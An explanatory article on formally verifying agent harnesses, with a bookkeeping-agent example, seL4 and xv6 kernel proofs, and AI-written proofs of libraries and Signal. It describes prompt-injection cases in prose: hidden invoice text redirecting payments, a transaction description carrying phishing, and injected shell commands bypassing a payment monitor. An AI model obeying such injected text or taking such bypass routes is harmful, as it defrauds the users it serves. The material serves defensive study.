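# Formal verification of critical paths in agent systems: what can and cannot be proved about tool-calling software

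## Tool-calling agents and what a formal proof says about them

Formal verification means proving mathematically that a program meets a precise statement of what it must or must never do. Engineers use it mainly where even a rare error would do serious harm, in operating systems, processors, compilers and cryptographic code, and in 2025 and 2026 a growing number of researchers applied it to AI agents. An agent is a language model run in a loop with tools, so its outputs cause actions such as sending a message, changing a file or paying a bill. Nobody can yet prove how the model will behave, but its output is only text until ordinary software reads it and acts on it. *Agent Safety is a Box*, by Brooker, an Amazon Web Services engineer who works on agents, bases its approach to safety on the fact that running the model changes nothing in the world and all the side effects come from the tools.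 People know a good deal about how to verify the software between the model and the tools.

### The path of a single tool call

Suppose an agent keeps the books of a small firm and has five tools. `read_email` fetches a message from the firm's inbox, `get_balance` returns the firm's bank balance, `request_approval` asks the firm's owner a question and returns the answer, `transfer_funds` pays an amount to an account and attaches a short reference text, and `run_shell` runs a command on the agent's computer. The owner asks the agent to pay the invoice that came from the paper supplier this morning.

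The harness, meaning the ordinary software around the model, combines the owner's request with a description of the five tools and sends both to the model. The model returns text containing a tool call, which is a structured request to run a named operation with given arguments, in this case `read_email` with a message number. The harness parses the text, meaning it finds the call, checks that the tool exists and that the arguments have the right types, and rejects anything malformed. A permission check then compares the call with a policy, a precise statement of which actions the agent may take and under what conditions. If the call passes, the harness executes it by contacting the mail server and adds the returned message to the text the model will read next. The loop then repeats. If nothing goes wrong, the model goes on to propose `get_balance`, `request_approval` and then `transfer_funds`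 with €412.80 and the supplier's account number, and finally tells the owner that the bill is paid.

The model only turns the text so far into more text. Ordinary programs parse its output, check permissions, run the tool and return the result. The critical path is the part of this code that every consequential action must pass through between the model's output and the action's effect.

Of the five tools, `run_shell` is the one that fits this picture badly. A check can read the payee and the amount from the arguments of `transfer_funds`, but the argument of `run_shell` is a string that may do almost anything once it runs. *Tether* (2026), which presents a monitor for agents that work in a terminal, treats this as a basic problem because earlier monitors assumed calls with known meanings and explicit targets, which shell commands lack.

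### How an invoice can misuse the agent

The model receives the owner's request and the supplier's invoice as parts of one text, and it may follow an instruction in either. Prompt injection is text in data the agent reads that the model follows as if it were an instruction. For example, if the invoice contains a note in white text on a white background that the supplier has changed banks and payment should go to a new account, the model may propose `transfer_funds` with the attacker's account number. Other hidden instructions could lead the model to put the firm's current balance in the payment reference, where the recipient can read it, or to propose a shell command that copies the inbox to an outside server. All of these calls are well formed. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) describes how a planted instruction can also steer an agent through a sequence of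 calls that each look ordinary but are harmful together.

Attackers already use invoices in this way. Infosecurity Magazine's *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* describes a case reported by the security company Barracuda. An invoice email contained hidden instructions for the AI summarising it to add a fake priority action to change a vendor's payment details, so that an employee would wire money to the attacker. In *How we helped Bunq secure their financial AI assistant*, Vissers and Van hamme (2026) describe sending a bank customer €0.02 with an injection in the description field. When the customer asked the bank's assistant about recent transactions, the assistant read the description and could then pass a phishing message to the customer.

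Developers have made prompt injection much harder. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports on a public competition in which 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models. Of these attempts, 8,648 succeeded. Every model was breached at least once, with success rates from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. These rates are closer to an upper bound than to a forecast, because participants could see the agent's whole conversation before writing their attack, which a real attacker usually cannot. Newer models do better. On a benchmark built from competitions of this kind, Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 gives a success rate of 0.1% for one attempt and 1.0% within 15 attempts. The most robust model from another company in that comparison had a rate of 9.2% within 15. Whether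 0.1% is low enough depends on what the tools can do and how easily the attacker can try again. Anthropic points out that an attacker can send the same email to a thousand inboxes.

### What a proof adds to testing

All of these figures come from tests, and a test that finds nothing is hard to interpret. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection* reports that attacks on Claude Opus 5 as a browser agent succeeded in none of 129 scenarios. Even if those scenarios were a random sample of all attacks, the true success rate could be as high as about 2.3% at 95% confidence, and they are not a random sample, because attackers look for whatever the testers missed. Willison (2026), commenting on 6,000 failed injection attempts, still advised against deploying an agent where an injection could do irreversible damage. Anderson (1972) made a similar point in *Computer Security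 Technology Planning Study*, written for the US Air Force, about "tiger teams", groups hired to break into computer systems. Anderson argued that if such a team fails, the security of the system is still unknown.

A proof can cover every case at once, but only if someone has stated exactly what the cases are. Suppose the owner wants the bookkeeping agent to pay out at most €1,000 in a session. The permission check keeps a number, *spent*, which starts at zero. When the model proposes a transfer of amount *a*, the check allows it and adds *a* to *spent* if *spent* + *a* ≤ 1,000. Otherwise it blocks the transfer and leaves *spent* unchanged.

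The specification, which is the statement to be proved about the system, is that the allowed transfers never add up to more than €1,000. The mathematical model of the system (a description, not a language model) consists of the starting value and the update rule just given. The theorem is that, for every finite sequence of proposed transfers, *spent* equals the total of the allowed ones and is at most 1,000. The proof is by induction. The statement holds at the start, when the total is zero. If it holds before a call, it holds afterwards, because the check either changes nothing or has confirmed that the new total stays within the limit. A computer program can check each of these steps. Testing cannot cover every sequence. With amounts in whole cents up to €1,000, there are about 10¹⁵ sequences of three transfers alone, and the theorem covers sequences of any length.

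The same example has two problems. First, the rule allows negative amounts. After a proposed transfer of −€5,000, the check would allow one of €6,000, bringing the total to €1,000, which satisfies the theorem. If the bank ignores the negative transfer and carries out the other, the firm loses €6,000. The proof is correct, but the specification is wrong. Second, the program may not behave as described. The description uses whole numbers of unlimited size, but integers in many programming languages wrap round to negative values when they grow too large, so a check written in such a language could let through an enormous payment. Anderson therefore asked for both a proof that the abstract design is secure and a demonstration that the implementation corresponds to it before anyone certified a system.

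Three kinds of program do most of the checking. A proof assistant, such as Lean, Rocq or Isabelle, checks every step of a formal proof that a person or an AI has written. It can handle almost any mathematical statement, but the proofs are long. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) uses about 31,600 lines of Isabelle for a theory of injection attacks and its application to 25 small example agents.

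An SMT solver, such as Z3, looks for values that satisfy a logical formula, or proves that none exist. To check the induction step above, an engineer uses it to search for values where *spent* ≤ 1,000 and *spent* + *a* ≤ 1,000 but the new total exceeds 1,000. There are none, so the step holds. If the programmer had mistakenly compared only *a* with the limit, the solver could have returned *spent* = 1,000 and *a* = 1, which can be used as a test case for the bug.

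Model checking explores every state that a (usually finite) description of a system can reach. In the bookkeeping agent, an approval might be absent, pending, granted or used. A model checker would try every order of events and, if a single approval can be used to pay two bills, print the shortest sequence in which that happens. The method needs little human effort, but the number of states grows very quickly with the size of the system. Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026) review 38 studies in *Toward Safe LLM Agents*. They name SPIN and NuSMV as standard model checkers and find that model checking is the most common algorithmic basis for work on agents.

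### Why the language model is not what gets proved

Nobody can currently prove that the model never follows an instruction in an invoice, though such a proof would be more satisfying. It would need a precise definition of "following an instruction" that fits every email a supplier might send, and nobody has one. The definition can't simply rule out any influence from the supplier's text, because the owner wants the agent to take the amount and the due date from the invoice. Even with a definition, the proof would have to cover a network with billions of parameters or more, which is far beyond existing methods for proving facts about neural networks. A proof for one set of parameters also would not carry over to the next release of the model.

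Brooker describes another obstacle to proving from the inside what an agent will do, one that better mathematics would not remove. People use agents because they cope with situations that nobody listed in advance, and such a proof would require constraining that flexibility. A limit outside the agent avoids the trade-off. If a deterministic check ensures that a refund never exceeds the purchase price and that each order gets at most one refund, the largest possible loss follows from those rules, whatever injection an attacker uses.

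Verifiers therefore usually assume that the model can return any value of the permitted type, and prove what the surrounding software does in response. The theorem about the spending limit has this form. It does not depend on why the model proposed a transfer, so it holds whether the model works as intended, makes a mistake or is controlled by an attacker.

### Properties of one run and of several

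What such a theorem can guarantee depends on the kind of property. A safety property states that something bad never happens, so any violation shows in a finite run. For the bookkeeping agent, one safety property is that no transfer above €200 goes out unless the owner has approved that payee and that amount. If the agent breaks this rule, the violation is a specific payment, and a check before that payment could have stopped it. The rule must state exactly what an approval covers. Dongol analyses an email agent in which an approval permits the next message with any content, so an injected call that arrives between the user's approval and the planned reply can use the approval to send private data. Tying the approval to the exact arguments prevents this, although an attacker who can time the replies may still learn a little.

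A liveness property states that something good eventually happens, for example that every invoice the owner asks the agent to pay is eventually either paid or reported as unpayable. No finite run refutes this, since the payment might still come. A permission check cannot guarantee it either, because the check can refuse a call but cannot make the model propose one. Safety alone is easy to achieve, because a check that refuses every call satisfies the €200 rule. Dongol notes the same of his own security criterion, so one has to establish separately whether the agent still completes its tasks. Brooker likewise holds that careful prompting and management of the model's context help with liveness but are insufficient for safety.

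The literature on agents uses these terms more loosely. Dantas and colleagues write π = (a₁, …, aₙ) for the sequence of actions in a plan, φ for a property, and π ⊨ φ for the claim that the plan satisfies the property. They call φ a safety property if it can be expressed in temporal logic, a notation for statements about "always", "eventually" and "until". This definition includes properties that no check of individual calls could enforce.

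Some requirements can only be checked by comparing runs. For example, the owner may want the supplier to learn nothing about the firm's balance. If a payment goes out with the reference "80412", one cannot tell from that run alone whether this is an invoice number or the balance in euros. One has to compare it with a second run that is identical except for the balance. If the reference changes along with the balance, information has leaked. The strictest requirement of this kind, noninterference, is that what the observer sees never changes with the secret. A list of forbidden calls cannot express this requirement, so a proof of it must follow data through the system.

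### The reference monitor and what it rests on

Most verified agent systems of 2026 share a design that Anderson set out in 1972. The Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and feared a malicious user who could run arbitrary programs on it. Anderson proposed a reference monitor, which checks every access to data, programs or devices against a list of what the user may do. The monitor had to be tamperproof, always invoked, and small enough for people to be sure that their analysis and tests of it were complete. A language model that has just read a stranger's email is in much the same position as the malicious user's program.

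Each requirement matters for the bookkeeping agent. If `run_shell` can edit the file that holds the spending limit, the agent can tamper with the monitor. If a shell command can contact the bank directly, using a password it finds on the disk, money can leave without a call to `transfer_funds`, and the theorem about *spent* stays true while the account empties. Preventing this requires complete mediation, which means that every effect on the world goes through the monitor. According to *Kairos* (2026), monitors placed where the harness dispatches tool calls are the weak point, because they check only the actions that the agent declares. Brooker relies on the network instead. The environment that runs the agent blocks all traffic except to one gateway, which applies the policy. Anderson observed that any program exempt from the checks becomes part of the security apparatus and has to meet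 the same standards as the monitor. One commercial operating system of the time was too large to qualify, because the part that would have had to serve as the monitor contained 200,000 to 300,000 instructions.

Papers on recent systems claim the three properties with different degrees of support. *Causality Laundering* (2026) describes ARM, a proxy between the model's client and the server that runs the tools. ARM runs in a separate process that the agent can't reach. Every call passes through it if, as the paper assumes, the deployment has no other path to the tools. To address the size requirement, the paper offers layers of deterministic rules that engineers can analyse and test one at a time. This makes a proof feasible, but the paper doesn't supply one.

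*Agenra* (2026) goes further by deploying the same functions whose properties its developers proved. Its Python code forwards each tool call to a core written in Lean, which checks the call against the state of the task and deducts any quota or approval before the tool runs. The paper also lists what it has to trust: the Python code that translates and carries the calls, the declarations of where data comes from, the verdicts of content scanners, and the behaviour of the external tools. Such a list describes the trusted base, meaning everything that must work correctly for a proved guarantee to hold in the running system. A component is called "trusted" because the guarantee depends on it, whether or not it is reliable.

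The trusted base also includes people. The core of *Agenra* confirms that an approval exists and that the call uses it up, but it relies on the reviewer to judge correctly. If the owner of the small firm sees a request to pay €412.80 to the paper supplier's new account, knows that an invoice is due, and clicks yes, the attack using the hidden note in the invoice succeeds even though every theorem still holds. Whether a payment is legitimate often depends, as *Kairos* puts it, on intent that the monitor cannot specify in advance.

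The rest of the base lies below the harness. Anderson assumed that the system identifies its users correctly, that guards and locks protect the machine, that the communication lines are secure and that the hardware works. He also wanted either compilers certified free of hidden trapdoors or an independent check of their output. The bookkeeping agent also relies on the operating system to keep its processes apart, and a verified kernel such as seL4 can replace some of that trust with proof.

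## Proofs about operating-system kernels and what they cost

An operating-system kernel is the program that controls a computer's hardware on behalf of every other program. It determines which memory each program can access, which program runs next and which messages pass between them. A bug in the kernel can let an attacker who controls one program take over the whole machine, so any guarantee about software that shares a computer with an untrusted program depends on the kernel.

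seL4 is a microkernel, meaning a kernel that keeps only the functions that need full control of the hardware and leaves file systems, network software and most device drivers to ordinary programs. It has about 8,700 lines of C and 600 lines of assembly code, small enough for the complete analysis that Anderson wanted for a reference monitor. In 2009 a research group in Sydney finished a machine-checked proof that the C code follows its specification. The seL4 project describes this as the first such proof for any operating-system kernel at the level of code. Klein, Andronick and colleagues, in *Comprehensive Formal Verification of an OS Microkernel*, cover both this proof and the group's later ones about the compiled program, access control and the flow of information.

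### From the specification to the machine code

The 2009 theorem concerns functional correctness, which means that the C code does only what the specification allows. The specification describes the effect of each operation on a simplified model of the machine. For example, when one program sends a message that another is waiting for, the message arrives and the receiver can run again. The C code must produce this effect with pointers, linked lists and packed bits.

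A refinement proof connects the program to its specification. The verifiers define a relation R that pairs each abstract state with the concrete states that represent it. They then prove that whenever (*a*, *c*) is in R and the program can step from *c* to *c*′, the specification allows a step from *a* to some *a*′ with (*a*′, *c*′) in R. If R also pairs their starting states, then by induction the specification allows every run of the program.

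The bookkeeping agent's spending limit shows how such a proof catches integer overflow. In cents, the abstract rule allows a transfer of *x* if *spent* + *x* ≤ 100,000. Suppose the program stores these numbers as 32-bit integers with a maximum of 2,147,483,647, and R holds when the two versions of *spent* are equal. If *spent* = 1 and *x* = 2,147,483,647, the abstract rule blocks the transfer, but the program's sum wraps round to −2,147,483,648. That is below the limit, so the program pays out more than €21 million. The proof fails because the specification allows no matching step.

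Comparing *x* with 100,000 − *spent* repairs the program, provided both versions also reject negative amounts. The proof of the repaired program relies on *spent* always lying between 0 and 100,000, because otherwise the subtraction could overflow too. A fact that holds in every reachable state is called an invariant. A kernel proof needs many invariants, for example that every pointer in a queue leads to a live object of the right kind. The seL4 team also wrote an executable specification between the abstract specification and the C code to make the gap manageable. Klein, Derrin and Elphinstone (2009) describe in *Experience Report* how they used Haskell for it.

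Refinement rules out crashes and undefined behaviour in the kernel. It also means that if someone proves the abstract specification never reaches a certain kind of unsafe state, the C code never reaches one either, and nobody has to reason about pointers again.

The original proof assumed that the compiler, the assembly code, the boot code and the hardware were correct. The group later removed the compiler from this list by proving that the kernel's compiled binary correctly implements its C source. If a compiler bug made this binary behave differently from the source, the proof would fail, so the group did not need to verify the compiler itself.

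### Capabilities, integrity and confidentiality

A kernel can follow its specification and still be insecure, because the specification might let any program read any memory. seL4 controls access through capabilities, which are unforgeable references to objects, such as pages of memory or message channels, that also carry rights to use those objects in certain ways. The kernel keeps all capabilities in its own memory, and a program refers to them only by their position in a table. If a program tries to send a message through slot 7, the request fails if that slot is empty or holds a capability that permits only receiving. A program on seL4 cannot name an object without a capability for it, whereas on most operating systems a program can name any file and the kernel then checks the user's permissions.

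Barthe (2026), in *Formalization of Security*, lists three security properties that the seL4 project has proved on this basis: integrity, authority confinement and a form of noninterference. Suppose an engineer runs the bookkeeping agent's shell and its payment code as separate programs on seL4, with a policy for which program may change what. Integrity means that while the shell runs, the only memory and objects that change are those the policy lets the shell change. Authority confinement means that no sequence of requests to the kernel can give the shell more authority than the policy allows. Without authority confinement, integrity would offer little protection, because a program could start with few rights and acquire more.

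Proving confidentiality requires comparing runs. Barthe describes the standard method, which Goguen and Meseguer introduced and called unwinding. Two states *s* and *t* are indistinguishable, written *s* ∼ *t*, if an observer cannot tell them apart. The verifier proves that a step taken from two indistinguishable states leads to two indistinguishable states. The verifier also proves that if a program that may not send information to the observer moves the system from *s* to *s*′ in one step, then *s* ∼ *s*′. By induction, these facts about single steps imply that whole runs look the same to the observer whatever the secret was.

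The seL4 proof establishes intransitive noninterference, which permits information to flow only along specified channels. Such a policy could let the shell pass text to a filter and the filter pass text to the network, but give the shell no direct route to the network. The kernel proof then guarantees that text from the shell can reach the network only through the filter. It does not cover whether the filter removes the right things. It also leaves out timing, so a program that can measure how long its operations take may still learn something about other programs.

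Ordinary refinement, the method that carried the other properties down to C, does not preserve confidentiality. Barthe makes this point about compilers. Suppose the bookkeeping agent's specification permits any five-digit number as a payment reference. The specification reveals nothing about the firm's balance, because every reference is possible whatever the balance is. A program that always uses the balance as the reference still refines this specification, since every number it produces is allowed, but it reveals the balance to anyone who sees the reference. The seL4 team therefore had to remove this kind of programmer's choice from the specification before a confidentiality proof about the specification could apply to the code.

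### Why the theorems hold for any program

These theorems hold whichever programs run on the kernel, whether a spreadsheet, a virus or a file of random bytes. The proofs assume that a user program can change its own registers and the memory it has access to in any way, and can make any request to the kernel with any arguments. The verifiers have to show that every possible step of a user program and every step of the kernel's own code preserves the kernel's invariant. For the user program's steps, they rely on the processor to block access to any memory that the kernel has not opened to the program, and for the kernel's steps, they analyse the code.

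Kernel designers made the arbitrary-output assumption decades before anyone needed it for language models. They had to contain programs they could not predict, and they did so without analysing them. The 2026 proof about PocketFlow, a small framework for building agents, treats the language model in the same way. However, a processor physically stops a program from writing to kernel memory, whereas a harness is protected from its model only as long as it treats the model's output only as text. Once the harness offers a tool like `run_shell`, the model can act on the machine that runs the harness, and the engineer needs something like a kernel to restore the boundary.

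A theorem that holds for all programs can only rule out actions that exceed a program's authority. For example, the 2026 proof about the xv6 kernel covers a sandbox in which a user can run an unverified program. Whatever that program does, it cannot corrupt the kernel or modify files, except files that it inherited already open. But it keeps access to the console, and the theorem leaves console output unconstrained from the moment the program starts until the next power cycle. No stronger guarantee about the output would be true, because an arbitrary program that may print can print anything. Likewise, if an arbitrary model may make payments, only the conditions on each payment limit the damage.

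### The price of the first proof

Lin (2026), summarizing the 2009 work in *Paper Notes*, reports that the proof took about 200,000 lines of Isabelle and about 11 person-years of effort specific to seL4. That is roughly 23 lines of proof for each line of C. The total was about 20 person-years, including the general tools and libraries the team also had to build. This is probably the source of the "twenty years" that some recent press reports give for seL4.

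Verification also constrained the kernel's design, and Klein and colleagues describe choices they made to keep the proof tractable. The kernel they verified ran on one processor core, with interrupts mostly disabled while kernel code was running. This avoids most cases of two pieces of kernel code working on the same data at once. A team that wanted such a proof had to design its software for verification, keep it small and change it rarely, since each change could invalidate part of the proof. Few projects accepted these constraints, and an agent harness, which its developers may revise every week, would have been a poor candidate.

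### The xv6 kernel in 102 days

xv6 is a small Unix-like kernel that universities use for teaching. Its developers did not write it with verification in mind. It runs on several cores, takes interrupts while kernel code is running, and includes a file system that has to survive power cuts. Kaashoek and Zeldovich (2026), in *Extending concurrent separation logic to the hardware level*, report a proof that covers all 6,657 lines of its C and assembly code. They took 102 days to get from the bare idea to the finished theorem, and used AI agents to help write the proofs and the intermediate specifications. The result is about 1.6 million lines of Rocq, or 240 lines of proof for each line of code.

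Their main theorem is about the text on the console. If a user types `echo hello world`, the system can print only `hello world` or one of a list of errors, such as a failure to start the program because memory has run out. The theorem also covers several other commands and combinations of them. For example, if the user stores the word "again" in a file and the machine restarts, a later command that searches the file for the letter "a" must print "again". The proof of these modest-looking claims has to cover the scheduling of eight cores, interrupt handling, the memory tables and disk recovery, because a mistake in any of them could make the claims false.

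The proof starts from the compiled kernel, as a sequence of bytes in memory, and the initial contents of the disk. Kaashoek and Zeldovich therefore do not need to trust the compiler, assembler or linker, and the proof includes the boot code and assembly code that the 2009 seL4 proof assumed to be correct. But they have to reason about 8,725 machine instructions on a detailed model of a RISC-V processor, in which even a single instruction consists of several steps that other cores and devices can interrupt.

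Considering every order in which these steps might happen would be hopeless. The proof uses concurrent separation logic, in which each part of the proof owns certain pieces of memory, and no other part may touch them in the meantime. A lock transfers ownership. If *l* is the memory location of a lock and *P* stands for ownership of the data it protects, the central invariant in a simplified version is

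∃*v*. *l* ↦ *v* ∗ ((*v* = 0 ∗ *P*) ∨ *v* = 1)

The arrow means that location *l* holds the value *v*, and the star means "and, separately". When *v* is 0, the lock is free and *P* is stored with it. When a core changes *v* to 1, it takes *P* and can work on the data as if no other core were running. It has to give *P* back to release the lock. The verifier can then check one function on one core at a time, and a general theorem about the logic extends the result to every order of events.

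A kernel never finishes, so the usual form of specification, a condition that holds when the program finishes, does not suit it. Kaashoek and Zeldovich instead prove that the processor can start from its power-on state and continue safely forever. Each function's specification is likewise that calling the function is safe if it is safe to continue from the state in which it returns. An agent's harness also runs in a loop of unknown length, so its central guarantee has to be an invariant too.

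The theorem is a safety property, so a machine that never printed anything would satisfy it. Kaashoek and Zeldovich ran the system in an emulator to confirm that it does print. They have not proved that every process keeps making progress, or that one process's secrets cannot leak to another, so in this respect the xv6 result is weaker than the one for seL4. The proof also assumes a particular model of shared memory, and the RISC-V standard permits processors that reorder memory accesses more freely than that model allows.

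The researchers found 11 bugs in xv6, some of which would crash the kernel. They also found a bug in the tool that translates the processor model into Lean, and another in the model itself, which comes from the organisation that maintains the RISC-V standard. The model is part of the trusted base, and they found its bug only because they were trying to prove a large theorem that relied on it.

If both authors worked every one of the 102 days, the effort was a little over half a person-year, compared with 11 person-years for seL4, not counting the cost of running the agents. The comparison is rough, because the theorems differ and the later project could build on years of research into separation logic and on an existing processor model. The human work was still substantial. Kaashoek and Zeldovich laid out the overall plan in detail and were heavily involved in designing the layers, abstractions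 and specifications, and their prompts to the agents contained about three times as much text as the paper. They did not have to read the proofs, because Rocq checks them, but they did have to make sure that the final theorem means what they intended.

### Proofs about compiled libraries

Anthropic and Theorem, a program-verification company, used AI-written proofs to establish a much simpler property of far more programs. According to РБК-Украина's *Скрытые ошибки в ПО*, a Russian-language news report, Claude proved that 239 entry points in 123 open-source libraries cannot fail under stated conditions. It puts the proofs, which are about compiled RISC-V code, at about 180 million lines in total and about 600,000 lines for a typical proof. Rocq checked all of them.

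The specifications came from fuzz tests, which feed a library large amounts of generated input to see whether it crashes. Claude turned each existing test into a mathematical statement about all the inputs that meet the conditions. This is a clever way to get a specification with little work, because developers had already decided which functions to test and how to call them, and almost everybody agrees that a library should not crash. It works less well for properties without such agreement, and a decoder that never crashes may still produce the wrong picture.

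The attempt to prove these statements uncovered hundreds of bugs. One, in an image decoder, appears only with about 64 MB of input and more than 2 GB of memory. A fuzzer is unlikely to find it, because fuzzers depend on running many small inputs quickly. In another, a counter drops below zero, which could make a decompression routine write outside its allotted memory. An agent that opens email attachments routinely uses such libraries, and a memory error in one of them could give an attacker control of the harness without having to manipulate the model.

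According to РБК-Украина, Claude also fixed bugs and wrote new proofs for the changed software. For agent systems this may matter more than the effort of the first proof, because it weakens the argument that verification suits only code that rarely changes. However, the guarantees cover only single-threaded programs with no separately loaded libraries, in a modelled Linux environment, and only the properties and inputs specified in each theorem.

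### Signal and the specification of a secret

Signal is a messaging application whose encryption protocol WhatsApp and Google Messages also use. In November 2026 Google DeepMind announced that its system AlphaProof Code had verified the cryptographic core of libsignal, the library that implements the protocol. The verification required specifying what it means for a conversation to be secure, which is far harder than specifying that a program should not crash.

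According to Libnanews' *Signal*, the theorems cover how two people establish a shared secret, even if one of them is offline, and how their devices keep changing the keys afterwards. They concern confidentiality, authentication and the protection of messages before and after an attacker temporarily obtains a device's keys. The proof relies on assumptions about what the basic cryptographic operations achieve. The result does not extend to the whole Signal application or to every phone, and an attacker who stays on the device can still read the messages there.

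Most of the work was connecting these statements to the compiled program. Tom's Hardware's *Google DeepMind AI engineers conjure mathematical proof of Signal's encryption protocol* gives about 1.2 million lines of Lean for the mathematical reasoning about the protocol and 5.3 million for showing that the binary's instructions behave accordingly. The agents first defined the processor's instructions, its memory and registers, and the behaviour of a Linux process. The proof depends on about 26,000 lines of specification and machine description, which Libnanews reports have to be taken on trust. That is only 0.4% of the total, but nearly three times the number of lines of code in seL4.

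ETV Bharat's *AlphaProof Code* (2026) gives more detail on how people and AI divided the work. People worked with several models to turn Signal's security goals into formal statements, and human experts reviewed every specification. Agents wrote the proofs, then audited the result and flagged about 1% of the codebase for a person to recheck. The project took four weeks. To test whether the specifications could catch real mistakes, the researchers put two previously fixed bugs back into a copy of the code. In both cases the system produced a machine-checked proof that the altered version was insecure. This is good evidence that the specifications are not so weak that any program would satisfy them, but two known bugs cannot show that the experts thought of every property that matters.

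The four weeks also leave out earlier work. UA.News' *Google DeepMind formally verifies part of Signal protocol* reports that previous verification of parts of the code sped up the project, and that DeepMind has not disclosed the project's cost. The researchers found no new vulnerabilities in the parts they verified.

### Where a proof stops

The proofs about xv6, the open-source libraries and libsignal all concern compiled code, which is closer to what the machine runs than source code is. *Scaling Verification of Cryptographic Software with Aeneas, Rust, and Lean* (Ho, Fournet and colleagues, 2026) reports proofs about source code only. They cover 16,700 lines of Microsoft's cryptographic library SymCrypt, including experimental extensions. A tool called Aeneas translates the Rust program into a mathematical function in Lean. This is possible because Rust's ownership rules already exclude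 many of the cases in which two parts of a program change the same memory, so the verifiers no longer have to reason about pointers. The proofs show that the code does not halt with an error and computes what the cryptographic standards require.

The proofs take 237,000 lines of Lean, about 14 for each line of Rust, compared with 240 for xv6. Source-level proofs leave more to trust, here the Aeneas translation and the Rust compiler. This tradeoff may make sense for a harness that changes often, since shorter proofs are quicker to repair and many programs use the same compiler. Here too, agents write the proofs on their own, but experts still have to design and review the formal versions of the standards and of special processor instructions.

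This gap between mathematics and running code matters more in some applications than in others. It mattered a great deal in differential privacy, which adds random noise to statistics so that they reveal little about any individual. According to a presentation by Lean (2026), an attack by Mironov defeated implementations of the method by exploiting how computers round numbers, although the theory was sound. The presentation also describes SampCert, a library with more than 12,000 lines of proof that its random samplers are correct. The developers wrote their own tool to extract the version that Amazon Web Services runs, so they have to trust that tool instead of the Lean compiler.

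AI helps more with writing proofs than with writing specifications. Writing proofs once took the most effort, and it suits an AI agent unusually well because the proof assistant rejects every wrong answer and the agent can try again. No program can reject a wrong specification in the same way. Metz, in *Cyber Defence*, reports on companies that hope to verify ordinary applications with AI in hours or days, but notes that someone must first specify how the application should behave. Designers also cannot anticipate everything that happens once people use it.

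### What an agent system can take from a kernel

A verified kernel can provide the complete mediation that the bookkeeping agent lacked. Suppose the engineer puts the payment check into a small program on seL4 and gives only that program the capabilities to reach the bank and to access the memory that holds the password. The shell runs separately, perhaps inside a complete Linux system, which seL4 can run as a guest while controlling its channels to the outside. Authority confinement then prevents any shell command, including an injected one, from obtaining a connection to the bank. The theorem about *spent* now covers every payment that leaves this computer, as long as the remaining trusted parts, such as the network driver, work correctly. An attacker who finds a copy of the password in an old email can still use it from another machine, where no theorem about this kernel applies.

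Capabilities are also a useful pattern for tools. Most harnesses give an agent a tool such as `transfer_funds` for the whole session, which is like letting a program name every file on the disk. The harness could instead create a capability to pay €412.80 to one account, once, and give the agent only that. An instruction hidden in a later email could then not change the payee or increase the amount. Refinement proofs now take so much less effort that it is realistic to verify the code that creates and checks such capabilities. That code is a few hundred or a few thousand lines, much smaller than xv6, and its developers can write it with verification in mind.

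The hard part is choosing the right account to pay. A kernel's specification refers to things that the kernel creates and records, such as pages of memory, channels and the rights to use them. The kernel's tables record whether the shell may write to a certain page, but not whether an account belongs to the paper supplier. At the level of the kernel, the correct payment and the fraudulent one are both a few hundred encrypted bytes that an authorised program sends through the same socket. A check in the harness can read the payee and the amount and compare them with a rule, but someone who knows whom the firm owes money has to supply that rule.

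## Proving the agent's control loop safe for any model output

Once there is a rule about whom the agent may pay and how much, the next task is to prove that the harness never breaks it, whatever the model proposes. *Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) gives a general method for such proofs and applies it to PocketFlow, an agent framework of about 100 lines. As far as Moon and Varshney know, this is the first deductive proof about an agent framework.

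### Replacing the model with an arbitrary value

Moon and Varshney write their program in Dafny, a programming language whose verifier uses an SMT solver to check code against specifications written alongside it. They represent the language model as a procedure with a declared result type and no body. The verifier has no information about the result except its type, so it has to prove that the rest of the program is safe for every value of that type. Verification researchers call this technique havoc.

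For the bookkeeping agent without its shell, the type might be

Action = ReadEmail(id) | GetBalance | RequestApproval(text) | Transfer(payee, amount)

The proof holds even for a model that has read the harness's source code and plans fifty calls ahead. Any plan amounts to choosing an action after each possible history, and the proof covers every sequence of actions. It also covers a model that chooses at random, since each run still produces one of these sequences.

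This also simplifies testing. *CONTINUITY* (2026) proposes contracts between the separate security controls of an agent system. Its design assumes that the model is hostile, so its test program creates the attacker's tool calls directly and never calls a language model.

The proof also assumes that the verified code receives a value of type Action. The model returns text, which a parser must first convert into that type. Moon and Varshney assume that the parser does only this. If the parser evaluates the text as Python code, the model can act on the computer before the verified code receives any action.

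### From single steps to every run

To say what "safe" means, Moon and Varshney describe the harness as a transition system. It has a set of states with a starting state, a set of actions that the model can propose, and a set of boundary events, which are the effects the harness can have on the outside world. A step

*s* —*a*/*e*→ *s*′

means that when the model proposes action *a* in state *s*, the harness may emit event *e* and move to state *s*′. If the harness refuses the action, *e* is an event with no effect. Every state needs at least one step for every action, so the harness cannot leave a proposal unhandled.

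The policy is a predicate Π(*s*, *a*, *e*, *s*′) that each step either satisfies or violates. Some rules depend on more than one of these four arguments. The rule that a payment must go to the payee in the proposed call compares *a* with *e*, and the rule that an approval disappears once the agent uses it compares *s* with *s*′.

Suppose the owner raises the bookkeeping agent's spending limit to €5,000, and the harness now pays a transfer of *a* only if *a* > 0 and *spent* + *a* ≤ 5,000. As before, it adds each payment to *spent*. If the model proposes €3,000, €2,500 and €2,000, the harness pays the €3,000, refuses the €2,500 because the total would reach €5,500, and pays the €2,000, which uses up the limit. An attacker can't get past the limit by splitting a theft into small payments, since out of a hundred proposals for €100 each, the harness pays only fifty.

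The owner cares about how much money has left the account, regardless of the value of the variable *spent*. Let *paid* be the sum of all payment events so far. The goal is to prove that *paid* ≤ 5,000 after every step, but direct induction fails. In a state with *paid* = 4,000 and *spent* = 0, the goal holds, yet the guard would allow another €3,000, raising *paid* to 7,000. The harness can never reach this state, but the verifier can't rule it out because it may assume only that *paid* ≤ 5,000 before each step.

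The way out is to prove something stronger:

*spent* = *paid* and *paid* ≤ 5,000

The theorem about the €1,000 limit already had this form, and the same induction works here. Each payment raises both numbers by the same amount and the guard keeps the new total within the limit, so the statement holds after any number of calls, even though the guard checks only one call at a time. The proof requires the harness to finish each check and update before it starts the next, a condition that parallel calls can violate.

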